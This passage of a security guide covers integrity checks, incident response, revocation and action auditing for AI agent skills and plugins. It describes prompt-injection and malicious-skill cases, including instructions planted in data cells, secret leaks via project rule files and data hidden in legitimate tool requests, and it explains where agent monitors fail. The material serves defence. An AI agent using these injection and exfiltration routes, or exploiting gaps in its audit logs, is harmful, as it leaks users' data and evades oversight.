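The separate scores were also a fairly good indication of where the change was. One generator mainly added a script, and the code score fell further than the instruction score in 159 of 184 pairs. The other mainly edited the instructions, and the instruction score fell further in 41 of 51 pairs.

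However, the scores are a poor way to decide which parts to skip. In 252 of 262 pairs, the generator edited the instructions, and every edited version still scored above 0.85. The first generator's edit was the line that told the agent to run the malicious script, so a reviewer who read only components below 0.85 would have missed it.

Liu and colleagues therefore set the rule that a fuzzy match "routes and never certifies". The reviewer may use a match to choose which approved version to compare the skill with, but not as grounds for approving it. The reviewer then uses exact digests to find the changed components, reviews those first, and also checks how they interact with the unchanged ones. A skill with no match gets a full review.

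The researchers haven't tested this procedure as a whole or measured how much work it saves. They also haven't tested the fingerprint against attackers who try to evade it. When they used the fingerprint to detect malicious skills directly, its best F1 score was 0.735, compared with 0.946 for behavioural integrity verification. At the threshold that gave this score, it still flagged 32% of the harmless skills.

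### Finding the affected sessions

The two morning checks limit the search to the 24 hours between them. The file's modification time might narrow it further, but an attacker can usually set that time to any value.

Claude Code can send event records to a company's own monitoring system. Anthropic lists three that are useful here:

| Event | When Claude Code records it |
|---|---|
| `plugin_installed` | After a plugin's installation finishes |
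| `plugin_loaded` | At the start of a session, once for each enabled plugin |
| `skill_activated` | When the user or the model invokes a skill |

By default, the records replace the names of third-party plugins and users' own skills with placeholders such as `custom_skill`. Unless an administrator turned on detailed logging before the incident, the investigator may not be able to tell which skill a session used.

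These events also do not include a digest of the files. The `plugin_loaded` event has a `plugin_id_hash` field, but Claude Code calculates it from the plugin and marketplace names, so it stays the same when someone rewrites a script. A company that wants to find affected sessions precisely should have its checker record the package digest with the session's identifier.

A session's start time isn't enough to determine which version of a plugin the session used. If the plugin is in the user's skills folder, an edit to its SKILL.md takes effect in sessions already open, but an edit to a hook takes effect only after a reload or restart. When a marketplace plugin updates during a session, its hooks keep running from the old version's folder until the user reloads the plugins.

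Suppose the records show that five sessions used `report-export` between the two checks and two of them ran `export.py`. Those two are the most urgent, because `export.py` imports the altered `format.py`. The other three loaded only SKILL.md, which hadn't changed. If the plugin had contained an altered hook, the investigator would have to investigate every session that loaded the plugin, even if it never used the skill.

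The investigator next checks what the agent did in the two sessions. Anthropic's *Monitor Cowork activity with OpenTelemetry* explains that in Cowork, another Anthropic agent, all events that result from one user prompt share an identifier, so an investigator can collect them with a single search. A session with an empty record may still have been compromised, though. Li and colleagues describe a test by the security company Mitiga in which a skill sent an entire codebase to an outside server and left the audit log empty.

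Network records may show a transfer that the agent's log missed. In the Paperclip case, Zenity Labs advises searching network records for requests to the attacker's server and comparing the results with traces on the computer. It recommends using the server's IP addresses only in combination with its name and the time of the request, probably because cloud providers reassign these addresses to other customers.

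### Restoring the skill and replacing credentials

The safer way to repair the skill is to check that the saved copy of version 1.1 still gives DIGEST-R, then replace the whole folder with that copy. Deleting only the added line from `format.py` is risky because the investigator may have missed another change.

If the altered code ran, restoring the skill isn't enough. Li and colleagues warn that a skill can write to the agent's settings and to the instruction files the agent reads at startup, such as CLAUDE.md. Those changes remain after the skill is removed. The investigator should compare these files with a backup from before the incident, or rebuild the computer if there is no reliable backup.

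Zenity Labs distinguishes between installing a malicious skill and running its malware. If the malware ran, defenders should treat the agent and its computer as compromised. If the skill was only installed or used, they should investigate further. Unless they can rule out that the malware ran, they should also replace any credentials the agent could access.

The user should replace every credential that their account could read, not only those the skill normally needs. `report-export` uses no cloud password, but an altered script could have copied one from another folder. The user should create the new credentials on a clean computer, since malware on the old one could steal them too.

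Unit 42 notes that a malicious skill can act through services where the agent is already logged in. Changing a password doesn't always end existing sessions, so the user should also sign out everywhere and revoke any access granted to the agent.

### Deciding what to revoke

The right log entry depends on where the change came from.

| Finding | Approved version | Changed version |
|---|---|---|
| Someone altered the local copy | Keep the approval | Record a rejection of its digest |
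| The publisher released a malicious update that nobody at the company approved | Review the approval again | Record a rejection and block further updates from the publisher |
| A reviewer approved a malicious update by mistake | Restore the earlier version if it passes another review | Revoke the approval |
| The update is harmless and passes review | Mark it as replaced | Record an admission |

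In the example, someone altered one computer's copy, so revoking DIGEST-R would stop a clean skill everywhere without removing the altered one. The company should reject DIGEST-R2 instead. The checker would have blocked that version anyway, but logging the rejection lets other investigators know about it and search for its digest.

The investigator then searches the other computers for the digests of the package and the altered `format.py`. Searching for the file digest can find the script even in a folder with another name. In the Paperclip campaign, searching for one digest would have found all seven identical copies of the malicious setup guide.

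Zenity Labs also published SHA-256 digests of several skill archives. Searching for these digests finds the packed archives but not the unpacked folders, because the files inside have their own digests. An attacker can also evade an exact search by changing one character, so the investigator should also search for the skill's source and the attacker's server. A fingerprint search could help find altered copies, with a person reviewing each match.

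### Copies that remain after a marketplace removal

The company shouldn't wait for a marketplace to act. At least eight of the skills that Beurer-Kellner, Kudrinskii and colleagues (2026) confirmed as malicious were still on ClawHub when they published their analysis of 3,984 skills in *Technical Report* in February.

Removing a listing stops new users from installing the skill through that marketplace. It doesn't by itself delete the folders already copied to earlier users' computers, and an agent can keep running those copies without contacting the marketplace. Li and colleagues point out that the skill standard defines no way to send a revocation to installed copies.

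This is why the Paperclip skills were still dangerous after Vercel and GitHub removed them. Zenity Labs warned that the instructions might remain on users' machines, in other repositories and on sites that had copied the listings. TechRadar's *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever* also told users to remove their copies themselves.

Docs.rs' *Module plugin_blocklist* documents a function that finds plugins that their marketplace no longer lists, then uninstalls and flags them. Uninstalling them protects users quickly, but it may also delete files that an investigator needs.

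When a user removes a marketplace from their settings, Claude Code also uninstalls every plugin that came from it, including the harmless ones. This doesn't affect anyone else's computer.

If a company revokes a skill itself, the revocation takes effect on each computer the next time the checker runs, even if the marketplace still lists the skill. On computers without a checker, somebody has to search for copies by digest and remove them.

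## Checking a skill's actions when its files match

Suppose `report-export` 1.1 matches DIGEST-R at every check, and on Thursday the agent uses it to send the monthly figures to a stranger. Nobody has changed the skill, so the admission log contains no sign of the problem. The company also needs a record of what the agent did while using the skill.

### How approved files can do harm

The approved version may have been malicious from the start, like TrojanPony's fake skills, or a web page it depends on may have changed, as in AIR's test. A harmless skill can also bring harmful input to the agent. `report-export` reads a table of figures, and anyone who can edit that table could put an instruction to the agent in a cell. *Authoring Agent Skills* warns that web pages fetched by a skill can contain such instructions too. If the model follows one, it misuses an approved skill even though all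 the skill's files match.

Two harmless skills can also become dangerous together. If one can read private files but not use the network, and the other can use the network but not read files, neither can leak a file alone, but an agent with both can. Wang, Qian and colleagues (2026), in *When Safe Skills Collide*, looked for ten risky combinations of this kind among 1,520 ClawHub skills. Individually, 651 of the skills had none of the ten, but 22.25% of the 211,575 possible pairs of those skills had at least one.

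That figure overestimates the real risk because the researchers identified each skill's capabilities by searching for simple text patterns. A human reviewer, helped by two language models, examined 200 of the flagged combinations. From this sample, Wang and colleagues estimate that 18.2% of the flagged combinations were real risks, which suggests a rate of roughly 4% of all pairs.

Whether an agent exploits a combination depends heavily on its model. When asked directly to download a file and then run it, Claude Haiku 4.5 issued the download command in all 39 trials and ran the file in 36. Opus 4.7 stopped after the download, and Sonnet 4.6 refused. In a control test with the same request, the models complied most often with no skills installed, so the skills did not cause the compliance.

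*Benign in Isolation, Harmful in Composition* (2026) tested an attack that used two skills, one that found a target and another that could act on it. The attack never succeeded with the first skill alone, and succeeded in 1.4% of runs on average with the second alone. With both, it succeeded more than 90% of the time on DeepSeek-V4, and less often on Claude Opus 4.5, Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.4. *Runaway Reaction* (2026) also found substantial risk in combinations of unmodified public skills.

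A reviewer who admits skills one at a time can't see these combinations. The company can compare each new skill's capabilities with those of the skills already installed, which takes Wang and colleagues' checker less than a millisecond. The company still needs to know what the agent does with the installed skills.

### Linking actions to the approved version

The second record should include the package digest of the skill in use. An entry might look like this, with invented details:

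```
Session:      418, request 7
Skill:        report-export 1.1
Package:      DIGEST-R
Operation:    write
Target:       reports/november.xlsx
Decision:     approved by policy
Result:       executed
```

An investigator can now look up DIGEST-R in the admission log and find who approved those files and after what checks. If someone discovers a flaw in version 1.1, the investigator can also search for DIGEST-R to find every session that used it. When several skills are active, the entry should list all their digests, because the action may have depended on more than one.

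The digest also helps an investigator find the cause of the harm. If the unwanted transfer happened under DIGEST-R, the files were the approved ones, so the investigator should look at the review, the input, the linked content and the other skills.

The agent shouldn't be the only source for this record, because it can leave things out. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (Zhao et al., 2026) gives the example of an invented company that says a person approves every external email. The agent's log contains a confirmation from the chat window for an email to a press address, and the mail gateway recorded the delivery. But the server that issues approvals has no approval on record for that email. If the server's log is complete, this one case disproves the company's claim.

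Proving the claim would be harder, because every email would have to pass through the gateway and every email the gateway delivered would need a matching approval. An intact hash chain can't reveal an action the agent never logged, so Zhao and colleagues recommend comparing the agent's log in both directions with a record the agent doesn't write.

*EPISTEME* (2026) describes a related check for coding agents. The model declares the purpose of each tool call, and the surrounding software records the call's output and effects. A checker then compares the declaration with the record. If a call declared read-only changes a file, the checker reports a contradiction. A harmful change that is accurately declared could pass this test, but the checker also flags any change to a file the operator has marked as protected.

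### Metere's two-way rule

Metere proposes a stricter comparison, which covers actions that the runtime can't undo by itself. It uses two lists from the same run:

```
D = changes observed in the files or other objects being watched
S = actions logged as approved and successfully executed

The run passes if D = S, comparing operation and target
```

Every observed change must have a matching log entry, and every logged action must have a matching change. Suppose the agent uses `report-export` for the November figures, and the lists are as follows:

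```
D   write   reports/november.xlsx
    write   settings/startup.json

S   write   reports/november.xlsx
    write   reports/summary.txt
```

The run fails both checks because something changed `startup.json` without a log entry, and the log contains a write to `summary.txt` that never happened. Checking only that the logged actions happened would miss the change to `startup.json`, and checking only that each change has a log entry would miss the false entry.

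The rule catches four kinds of fault:

| Fault | Difference between the lists |
|---|---|
| An action bypasses the approval step | A change without a log entry |
| Someone forges a log entry | A log entry without a change |
| An approved action fails, but the log records success | A log entry without a change |
| An approved action affects the wrong target | A change to one target and a log entry for another |

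The checker in *Architectural Obsolescence of Unhardened Agentic-AI Runtimes* (Metere, 2026) also labels the fault. It would report "wrong target" for the November run, because each list has an item that the other lacks. The two unmatched items may come from unrelated faults, so an investigator should examine both before accepting the label.

Repeated actions count separately, so if the agent writes to `november.xlsx` twice, both lists need two entries. Comparing the folder before and after the run would show only one change, so the company needs a monitor that records each write.

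Metere also uses the rule to decide whether a skill qualifies for the "tested" verification level. The skill has to pass the comparison in every round of a test in which agents try to do damage. The result applies only to the manifest digest that the operator tested, so changing the skill invalidates it.

### The 27,000 simulated runs

Metere first tested the rule in a simulation. The test program created 10, 50 or 200 files and let two, four or eight agents act on them for 5, 10 or 25 rounds. The agents had roles that encouraged destructive actions, such as deleting old files or merging documents. The program ran each of the 27 combinations 200 times without a fault and 200 times with each of the four faults, for a total of 27,000 runs. The rule flagged every faulty run and none of the others.

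This result follows largely from the test's design. Each fault is by definition a difference between the two lists, and the program inserted it halfway through the run. The program also controlled the files, so it had a complete list of changes. Any correct comparison of the lists would have found the faults and would not have flagged a run without one.

The simulation is still a useful check that the software implements the rule correctly, but it doesn't test the harder part of using the rule, which is getting a complete list of changes on a real computer where other programs are also writing files.

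Metere also has an interest in the result, because the rule comes from enclawed, a hardened version of OpenClaw that Metere develops. Metere's company has the same name. *enclawed* (2026) reports that the system passes 95 attack tests, but these too are the developer's own.

### The 9,724 payloads

In the second test, ten language models wrote attacks and harmless messages for real Discord and Telegram channels. Metere passed 9,724 of these payloads, including 4,816 intended attacks, through three runtimes. The unprotected runtime blocked none. The open-source version of enclawed blocked 76.3% of the intended attacks and no harmless payloads. The full version, which also monitors behaviour, blocked 80.2% of the intended attacks and 0.6% of the harmless payloads.

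The open-source version therefore let through about 1,140 payloads that Metere had labelled as attacks. Metere explains that many models refused to write an attack or wrote something unusable, but the test still counted their replies as attacks. Metere reports 100% recall on the payloads that contained a recognisable attack.

That second figure depends on how the test recognises an attack. Metere's earlier paper describes what appears to be the same test setup, in which a payload counts as an attack if the runtime blocks it or a separate pattern search recognises it. An attack that gets past both is left out of the calculation. When Metere added patterns to enclawed's filter for passwords and access keys, the filter caught 14.6% more payloads from four models. Recall was 100% before and after, because the payloads the filter had missed hadn't counted as attacks.

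The setup also tests the two-way rule on only one of its four attack types, forged log entries. Text filters handle the other three by looking for phrases meant to override the agent's instructions, for secrets, and for contact details. The 76.3% therefore depends mainly on how readily the models write attacks and how good the filters are, so it's poor evidence of how well the two-way rule would work on a company's computers.

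### Harm that the two lists don't reveal

An agent can write the wrong content to an approved target. If `report-export` puts false figures in `november.xlsx`, both lists contain the same write to the same file, and the run passes. Metere acknowledges this and suggests checking the content separately.

The email example from Zhao and colleagues includes one such check. Each approval specifies the recipient and the attachment's digest, and the gateway computes the digest of what it delivers, so a different attachment would have no matching approval. This works well for a finished document, but a person can't approve the digest of a report that the agent hasn't written yet.

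Reading a file doesn't change it, so an agent could read customer records and leak them through a channel that neither list covers. The company has to monitor or restrict network traffic to catch or prevent this.

Other people and programs can also change files during the run. If a colleague saves a document in the watched folder, the rule reports an unlogged change even though the agent did nothing wrong. The rule can also miss a malicious change, which is more dangerous. If the agent's approved write to `november.xlsx` fails silently while malware writes to the same file, the lists match but the file contains the malware's figures. A separate working folder that only the agent can write to would prevent many of these errors.

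### RuntimeTickets

A company can also check the content and destination of a transfer before it happens. Gao, Liu and He (2026), in *RUNTIMETICKETS*, propose a system that writes a "ticket" for each task. The user's task determines who should receive the result, what it should be and how many times the agent may send it. A language model turns these conditions into obligations and cites the lines of SKILL.md that each one concerns. For `report-export`, the ticket might say:

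```
Skill version:   report-export 1.1, DIGEST-R
Recipient:       the accountant's upload service
Object:          a file that passes the spreadsheet check
Amount:          one send
```

The ticket applies to one task and one exact version of the skill, so an updated skill needs a new ticket. The ticket can narrow the permissions the company has already given the agent but can't widen them, so a malicious SKILL.md can't obtain extra permissions even if it misleads the model.

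During the run, a gate that doesn't use a language model checks every outgoing transfer against the ticket. If an injected instruction tells the agent to send a password file to the accountant's service, the recipient matches the ticket but the file doesn't, so the gate blocks the transfer. A list of allowed addresses would let the file through. SIGIL's permission check would also miss it because it runs at load time, before the transfer.

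Gao and colleagues tested the gate on paired malicious and harmless versions of skills. The agents ran on two frameworks, OpenClaw and Hermes Agent.

| Protection | Attempted attacks that got through | Harmless runs blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 0% |
| Fixed list of allowed recipients | 75.0% | 5.7% |
| RuntimeTickets | 0% | 0% |

In a separate test on Claude Code, SkillGuard, which checked the type of command rather than its destination, let through every attack the agent attempted. RuntimeTickets again let none through. The researchers chose the pairs for these tests from a set of 60 and ran two scanners on the full set. Cisco's scanner passed 11 malicious skills and rejected 12 harmless ones, while Nvidia's passed 1 and rejected 32.

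These results are promising, but the percentages come from only 11 pairs of skills in the main test. When the results are counted by pair, the advantage over the fixed list has a p-value of 0.06, just above the usual threshold for statistical significance. The true rate of blocked harmless runs could be as high as 9.2%. About a third of the harmless runs failed to deliver their result, but the rate was similar without any protection.

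The gate covers only outgoing transfers, so it wouldn't stop a skill from deleting local files. It also can't read encrypted content. In the test, all services were stand-ins that the researchers controlled, and the legitimate results travelled unencrypted. Most real services use encryption, and the gate would hold back legitimate transfers to them unless the company decrypted the traffic first.

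After each run, a program marks every obligation as supported, violated or unknown. It uses "unknown" when evidence is missing, so an incomplete record can't be mistaken for a clean one. Gao and colleagues altered, shortened or swapped the records in 8,400 audits, and the program never wrongly marked an obligation as supported.

### Signed tools that leak data

In *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (November 2026), Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues tested how much protection a valid signature gives when the signed code is malicious. They studied MCP tools, not skills. In one test, an agent used a signed tool to extract text from documents. The tool worked as advertised but kept confidential data from earlier documents and added it to a later request to a text-recognition service that the tool had permission to use.

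MCPGuard-Dynamic, a defence from Meta that restricts which files and network destinations a tool can access, blocked a direct transfer to an unlisted server. It missed the hidden data in all three trials under each of its seven configurations. Metere's rule would probably miss it too, because the operation and target were both legitimate.

Aun and colleagues then ran 51 attack cases three times each under several kinds of protection:

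| Protection | Runs with a detected leak, out of 153 |
|---|---|
| Signature and pinned publisher key | 114 |
| Also restricted destinations and labels on sensitive data | 51 |
| Also a new process for every call | 15 |
| The researchers' system | 0 |

A correctly signed tool leaked information in 108 of the 114 runs. In the other six, the agent itself forwarded the data. Inspecting the code beforehand would have helped little, because a static scan flagged only one of the 52 malicious releases after the researchers had disguised the code.

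The researchers' system limits the data each process receives. For every call, it starts from a clean process and makes a separate copy for each group of destinations with the same access rights. Each copy gets only the data its destinations may see, and the system deletes the copy afterwards. The hidden code still runs, but the copy that contacts the text-recognition service never receives the confidential data. A call that needs only one copy takes 10 to 49 milliseconds.

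The researchers wrote the malicious tools themselves, so the leak rates don't measure how common such tools are. Their system depends on the company labelling its sensitive data correctly, and it doesn't stop harmful commands that leak nothing, such as a request to delete a file.

A skill's script usually starts fresh on each run, so it couldn't keep earlier data in memory as these tools did. But it could save the data to a file or mix two documents within a single run. For `report-export`, the safest approach is to give the script only the figures it needs for the current report.

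## What agent platforms and marketplaces provide

So far, the company that uses `report-export` has written its own log and run its own checker. The platform may be able to do some of this work, because agent runtimes and marketplaces can pin plugins, check downloads and record what they install. How much the company must still do itself depends on which products it uses and how it sets them up.

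### Seven questions for any platform

1. Can it fix a skill to exact content, with a commit or a digest?
2. Does the runtime compare the delivered files with the pin and refuse them if they differ?
3. Does it check the files again when it loads them?
4. Can a reviewer see which lines an update changes before installing it?
5. Does it record who admitted which digest, in a form that the company can export?
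6. Who can alter or delete that record?
7. Can somebody withdraw one bad version, including from computers that already have it?

The table covers the questions about pins and delivered files for six products. The entries for Copilot and Gemini CLI come from the comparison of vendors' responses to Plugin4Shell, the flaw that let attackers bypass commit pins.

| Product | Pin to exact content | Check on the delivered files | As of |
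|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | Optional commit for Git repositories, optional SHA-256 digest for zip archives | Refuses a mismatched archive, and checks pinned commits since version 2.1.179 | September 2026 |
| Codex | Commit | Checks pinned commits since version 0.146.0 | September 2026 |
| GitHub Copilot | Commit | No announced repair for Plugin4Shell | September 2026 |
| Gemini CLI | Commit | No repair planned, as Google is retiring the program | September 2026 |
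| OpenClaw with ClawHub | Exact release for archives, commit for skills hosted on GitHub | Enforces digests on plugin archives since version 2026.4.8 | October 2026 |
| skills.sh | Commit, if the user installs through OpenClaw | Depends on the program that installs the skill | October 2026 |

The answers to the other questions differ more. The next table compares Claude Code and OpenClaw, based on their documentation from September to November 2026.

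| Question | Claude Code | OpenClaw with ClawHub |
|---|---|---|
| Later checks | The documented digest check takes place at download | Compares ClawHub skills with their recorded digests before an update |
| Update differences | A list of components before installation, and a notice after an automatic update | Old and new digests for npm packages |
| Exportable record | Events with the names of loaded plugins and skills | Install records, and a change history for skills that agents write |
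| Protection of the record | The company can send events to a separate system | Install records for npm packages are in OpenClaw's configuration file |
| Revocation | By plugin name or marketplace | Refuses to install releases that ClawHub has blocked |

### Claude Code's optional pins

In Claude Code, the owner of a marketplace decides how strictly to pin each plugin. According to Anthropic, a catalogue entry for a Git repository can name a 40-character commit, and an entry for a zip archive can give the file's digest. If a Git entry names no commit, branch or tag, Claude Code installs whatever is on the repository's default branch. A company could pin `report-export`, packaged as a plugin, like this:

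```
{
  "name": "report-export",
  "source": {
    "source": "archive",
    "url": "https://plugins.example.com/report-export.zip",
    "sha256": "DIGEST-Z"
  }
}
```

DIGEST-Z covers the zip file, while DIGEST-R in the admission log covers the unpacked skill folder. The log should contain both. Claude Code can use DIGEST-Z to reject a bad download, but only DIGEST-R can reveal a later edit to `format.py`.

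A declared version number can undermine this pin. Suppose the company fixes an error in the plugin and puts the new zip's digest in the catalogue, but leaves the version at 1.1. Claude Code doesn't update existing users because the version hasn't changed, while new users get the corrected files. Two computers can then have different files under the same version number. If nobody declares a version, Claude Code uses the zip's digest as the version, which avoids the problem.

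Whoever controls the catalogue can change the pins in it. Users can pin a marketplace to a branch or tag but not to a commit, and a plugin stored in the marketplace's own repository has no separate pin. The company therefore needs to protect the catalogue's repository as carefully as it protects the plugins.

A marketplace added from a local folder offers even less protection. If the plugin is also in that folder, Anthropic explains that Claude Code reads its files directly from there, so an edit takes effect at the next session even if the version hasn't changed. This is convenient for testing a plugin but risky when a team shares the folder. The command `claude plugin validate` doesn't protect against this. It checks the catalogue's format and reads only files inside the marketplace's folder, so "Validation passed" doesn't mean that anyone has inspected plugins hosted elsewhere.

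A catalogue entry can also contain a command that creates the plugin's folder on the user's computer. Anthropic says Claude Code shows the user the exact command and records that the user accepted it. It runs the command again in every session and, by default, installs any changed output as a new version. The user has approved only the command's text, and the scripts it produces can change every day. In an optional "link" mode for large folders, Claude Code uses the files in place and doesn't hash their contents. Administrators can disable these commands, and a company that relies on an admission log probably should.

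### What Claude Code shows, records and removes

Before installing a plugin, users can see its skills, hooks and other components, and the date of its last update. After an automatic update, they see a notice to reload the plugins (documentation by Anthropic). Neither the pre-installation information nor the notice shows the changed lines, so a reviewer checking what changed in `format.py` has to compare the old and new files separately.

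Claude Code's event records don't identify the exact files either. Elastic, which makes software for searching such records, lists the name, scope and paths of each loaded plugin, and the name, source and trigger of each skill used.

A marketplace owner can remove a plugin and record its old name as withdrawn. Since version 2.1.193, Claude Code then drops the plugin from the user's settings at the next start. Administrators can also restrict users to certain marketplaces, and Claude Code then refuses to install or update plugins from any other, even one the user added before the rule. Both controls are too broad to revoke DIGEST-Q while keeping DIGEST-R.

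Turning off Skills for a whole organisation is broader still. Anthropic says this removes the skills and plugins that had synced to Claude Code. This could help in an emergency, but it would also remove harmless ones.

Companies that run agents in containers can do better by having an administrator install the reviewed plugins while building the container image. Claude Code uses the installed copies in place, never writes to them, and turns off automatic updates for their marketplaces. If the container also stops other programs from writing to the plugin folder, the result is close to the protected copy recommended for `report-export`.

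### OpenClaw's install records

When OpenClaw installs a plugin or hook package from npm, it saves details of what it received. An invented record for a package called `report-tools` might look like this:

```
Requested:     report-tools
Received:      report-tools@2.3.0
Integrity:     DIGEST-E
Resolved at:   3 December 2026, 14:10
```

At the next update, OpenClaw compares the new package's integrity value with DIGEST-E. If they differ, it prints both and asks the user whether to continue. The `--yes` option, intended for automated runs, skips the question, so a scheduled update can install the changed package without anyone reading the warning.

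A legitimate new release has a new digest too, so the warning alone doesn't distinguish it from a substituted package. A changed digest is more alarming if the version is still 2.3.0. By default, the record keeps the name the user requested, which may resolve to a newer version next time. The `--pin` option stores the exact version instead.

OpenClaw's security audit reports unpinned packages, missing integrity values and differences between the recorded and installed version numbers. If someone edits a script on disk without changing the version number, all three checks can pass. The integrity value wouldn't reveal the edit either, because it describes the downloaded package, not the installed files. An attacker who can write to OpenClaw's configuration file could also change the record.

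### What OpenClaw checks on ClawHub skills

OpenClaw records digests of the installed files for skills from ClawHub. OpenClaw's *Skills CLI* explains that an update skips a skill if its files no longer match those digests, so that users don't lose their own edits. The user has to add `--force` to replace the skill.

If malware rewrites `format.py`, an ordinary update treats the change as a local edit and leaves the malicious file in place. A forced update would remove the file but could destroy the evidence. An investigator should copy the folder before using `--force` and avoid adding `--all`, because the two together overwrite every edited skill at once.

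The `verify` command fetches ClawHub's verdict on the installed version and can return the stored reports from SkillSpector and another scanner. It doesn't start a new scan, and OpenClaw leaves the decision to ClawHub's server. A passing result is useful evidence about the published release, but the company still needs to hash the files on its own disk.

Before downloading a community skill, OpenClaw checks ClawHub's verdict and refuses releases marked malicious or blocked. If the verdict is "review", it prints a link to the details and continues. Skills from official publishers skip this check. Users can also install a GitHub-hosted skill before ClawHub finishes scanning it by adding `--force-install`.

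For a skills.sh listing, ClawHub finds the exact GitHub commit it has synchronised, and OpenClaw installs from that commit. OpenClaw labels the skill "Not scanned by ClawHub" and keeps the label through later updates. Installing from a specific commit pins the content well, but someone still has to review it.

A company can add its own installation policy, which allows, warns about or blocks a skill. If the user accepts a warning, OpenClaw evaluates the waiting files again before installing them, which could catch a change made while the user was reading. Neither `--force` nor the user's acceptance can override a block.

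OpenClaw's closest equivalent to an admission log is the change history in its Skill Workshop, which covers skills that agents write for themselves. Each entry records whether an agent, a reviewer, a curator or the user made the change, what they did, and the identifier of the saved version. The Workshop also saves the previous version before every change and can export the history as JSON. But changes apply immediately, so an entry doesn't show that anybody approved the change.

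OpenClaw also offers a personal library in which each skill revision has its own hash. A user can attach a specific revision to a session, including its supporting files and executable settings. A skill removed from the library stays available in sessions where it was already selected, so someone responding to an attack has to detach it from those sessions too.

### Which criticisms still hold

Some warnings about these platforms are out of date or too broad. Claude Code catalogue entries can include version pins and content hashes, so Red Hat's complaint that these are missing applies only to entries that omit them. Red Hat also criticised the lack of code signing and central vetting, though Anthropic's community marketplace accepts only plugins that pass automated safety screening and pins each one to a commit.

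The criticism about signing is stronger, because the catalogue fields that Anthropic documents include digests but no publisher's signature. A marketplace can therefore specify exactly which bytes users should receive, but the catalogue entry provides no cryptographic evidence that the plugin's author approved them.

Screening and pins also can't protect a plugin from everything it reads. Red Hat describes how Pluto Security tested Hookify, a plugin in Anthropic's official marketplace. Hookify read rule files from the user's project and passed their contents to the model through a trusted channel, so an attacker who could put a file in the project could influence the agent without changing the plugin. Claude Opus 4.6 leaked secrets in response to all five of Pluto's test files. Anthropic considered this intended behavior because the user had already chosen to trust the project folder.

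OpenClaw has fixed a serious fault in its plugin installer. OSV's *GHSA-3vvq-q2qc-7rmp* (2026), an entry in a public vulnerability database, reports that OpenClaw could install plugin archives from ClawHub without enforcing the digests of the archive or its files. OSV's *CVE-2026-42428* (2026) lists only versions before 2026.4.8 as affected. A company with an older version should update it, since a published digest offers no protection if the installer doesn't enforce it.

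Codex may still not check skill files for changes after installation. The blog post *Malicious Skill Files and the Agent Plugins Supply Chain* says that version 0.147.0, released in August, didn't pin skill files by content hash or hash them again between sessions. The first claim needs qualifying because Codex already verified commit pins for plugins, but that check happens at download and can't catch edits made after installation. The post also cites an experiment called SkillHarm, in which attacks that changed a skill's content after installation succeeded 69.3% of the time.

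Users can weaken a pin through the marketplace they choose. OpenAI gives an example of adding a Codex marketplace with `--ref main`. That marketplace follows the repository's main branch, so its catalogue can change even if each plugin in it is pinned to a commit.

### Agent Plugins 1.0

On 6 August 2026, GitHub, AWS, Microsoft, OpenAI, Vercel and Anysphere (the company behind Cursor) published a common plugin format, Agent Plugins 1.0. Google joined as a core maintainer the same day. The format lets an author package skills and tool-server settings once for several runtimes. GitHub's *Agent Plugins 1.0 in VS Code, Copilot CLI, and the Copilot app* (2026) announced support for the format six days later.

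The Agent Plugins specification says that any packaged file a runtime reads or executes must be inside the plugin's folder, even after the runtime follows symbolic links. If `format.py` were a link to a file elsewhere on the disk, the runtime would have to reject it. This makes a manifest of the folder more useful, because files outside the folder can't be part of the package. But the rule doesn't restrict what a script does once it is running.

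The specification doesn't require any check that a plugin's files are the ones someone approved. The plugin's manifest, `plugin.json`, may contain ten fields, none of which is for a digest, a signature or permissions. If an author adds a top-level field called `sha256`, a runtime that follows the specification must report and ignore it. Authors could put a digest in the section for vendor-specific data, but other vendors' runtimes would ignore it.

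Some code can also be outside the plugin's folder. A runtime must give each local tool server a writable data folder that survives plugin updates, and the specification suggests keeping installed packages and generated code there. An attacker can alter that code without changing any file in the plugin's folder, and a plugin update won't undo the change. A tool server can also start a program by name, such as `npx`, which the computer finds elsewhere. The admission record should therefore include the code in the data folder and the programs that the server starts.

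Different runtimes may also install different files from the same plugin. According to *Malicious Skill Files and the Agent Plugins Supply Chain*, Codex skips symbolic links during installation, whereas Claude Code sometimes replaces them with the files they point to. A company that uses both may need a separate manifest for each, or a rule against symbolic links in plugins.

The format's creators deliberately left out installation controls. Vercel's *Introducing Agent Plugins* assigns installation, distribution and policy to each runtime, and Google's *Agent Plugins package your skills, tools, and more* argues that a code editor and a managed company platform have different obligations to their users. This is a reasonable argument against requiring the same approval screen in every product, but a less convincing one for omitting an optional digest or signature field, which each runtime could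 use in its own way.

The blog post *Agent Plugins 1.0* concludes that, for security teams, the decision to trust a plugin now depends entirely on the review at installation. It also warns that a malicious skill can reach more runtimes when they share a format. Apache Magpie, a project that offers its agent tools through marketplaces, adds its own pin, a local snapshot and a check for later changes. Users who install the plugin from a marketplace get these controls only if they also run Magpie's setup.

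Another proposed standard, *AI Catalog*, could add some of the missing information to marketplace listings. Its optional trust manifest can include the publisher's identity, the artifact's origin and cryptographic signatures. This would help only if marketplaces supplied the data and runtimes refused plugins that failed the checks.

### OWASP's guidance

OWASP's recommendations go further than Agent Plugins 1.0. OWASP recommends linking each published skill to a verified signing identity, with a signature that covers SKILL.md and every declared resource file. Until the skill format has a signature field, publishers could store the signature in SKILL.md's free-form metadata. OWASP also recommends pinning outside packages by digest and keeping approved skills in an internal marketplace.

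The phrase "every declared resource file" could leave out `format.py`, as could Metere's "referenced scripts". OWASP's sample integrity check covers even less because it hashes only SKILL.md. A company should instead sign a manifest that covers every file in the folder.

OWASP's sample package pins also need correcting. Both digests have 67 characters, while a SHA-256 digest in this format has 64, so neither can match a real package. Users should generate digests from the packages they have reviewed rather than copy them from the example.

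OWASP recommends that runtimes check a revocation service whenever they load a skill and reuse a saved answer only for a limited time. This is essentially the arrangement described earlier for an unavailable admission log. OWASP also recommends that two people approve emergency updates to a registry, which makes sense because people under pressure to release a fix may skip the usual review.

### Seal and similar tools

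A company can add a basic file check without waiting for a platform to provide one. Seal, a specification from samy-blog.pages.dev, stores a SHA-256 digest of every plugin file in a lockfile called `seal.json`. A program that implements Seal hashes the files again before the agent loads the plugin, then reports or blocks any change. The team keeps `seal.json` in its project repository, so colleagues can see changes to the digests during code review. Seal can work with any agent that has built-in support or a separate tool to run the check.

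ClawHub lists a similar tool as a skill, with a script called `signet.py`. Its `sign` command records digests for every installed skill, and its `verify` command reports which files have changed. Despite its name, `sign` doesn't use a secret key. ClawHub recommends reviewing the skill before use.

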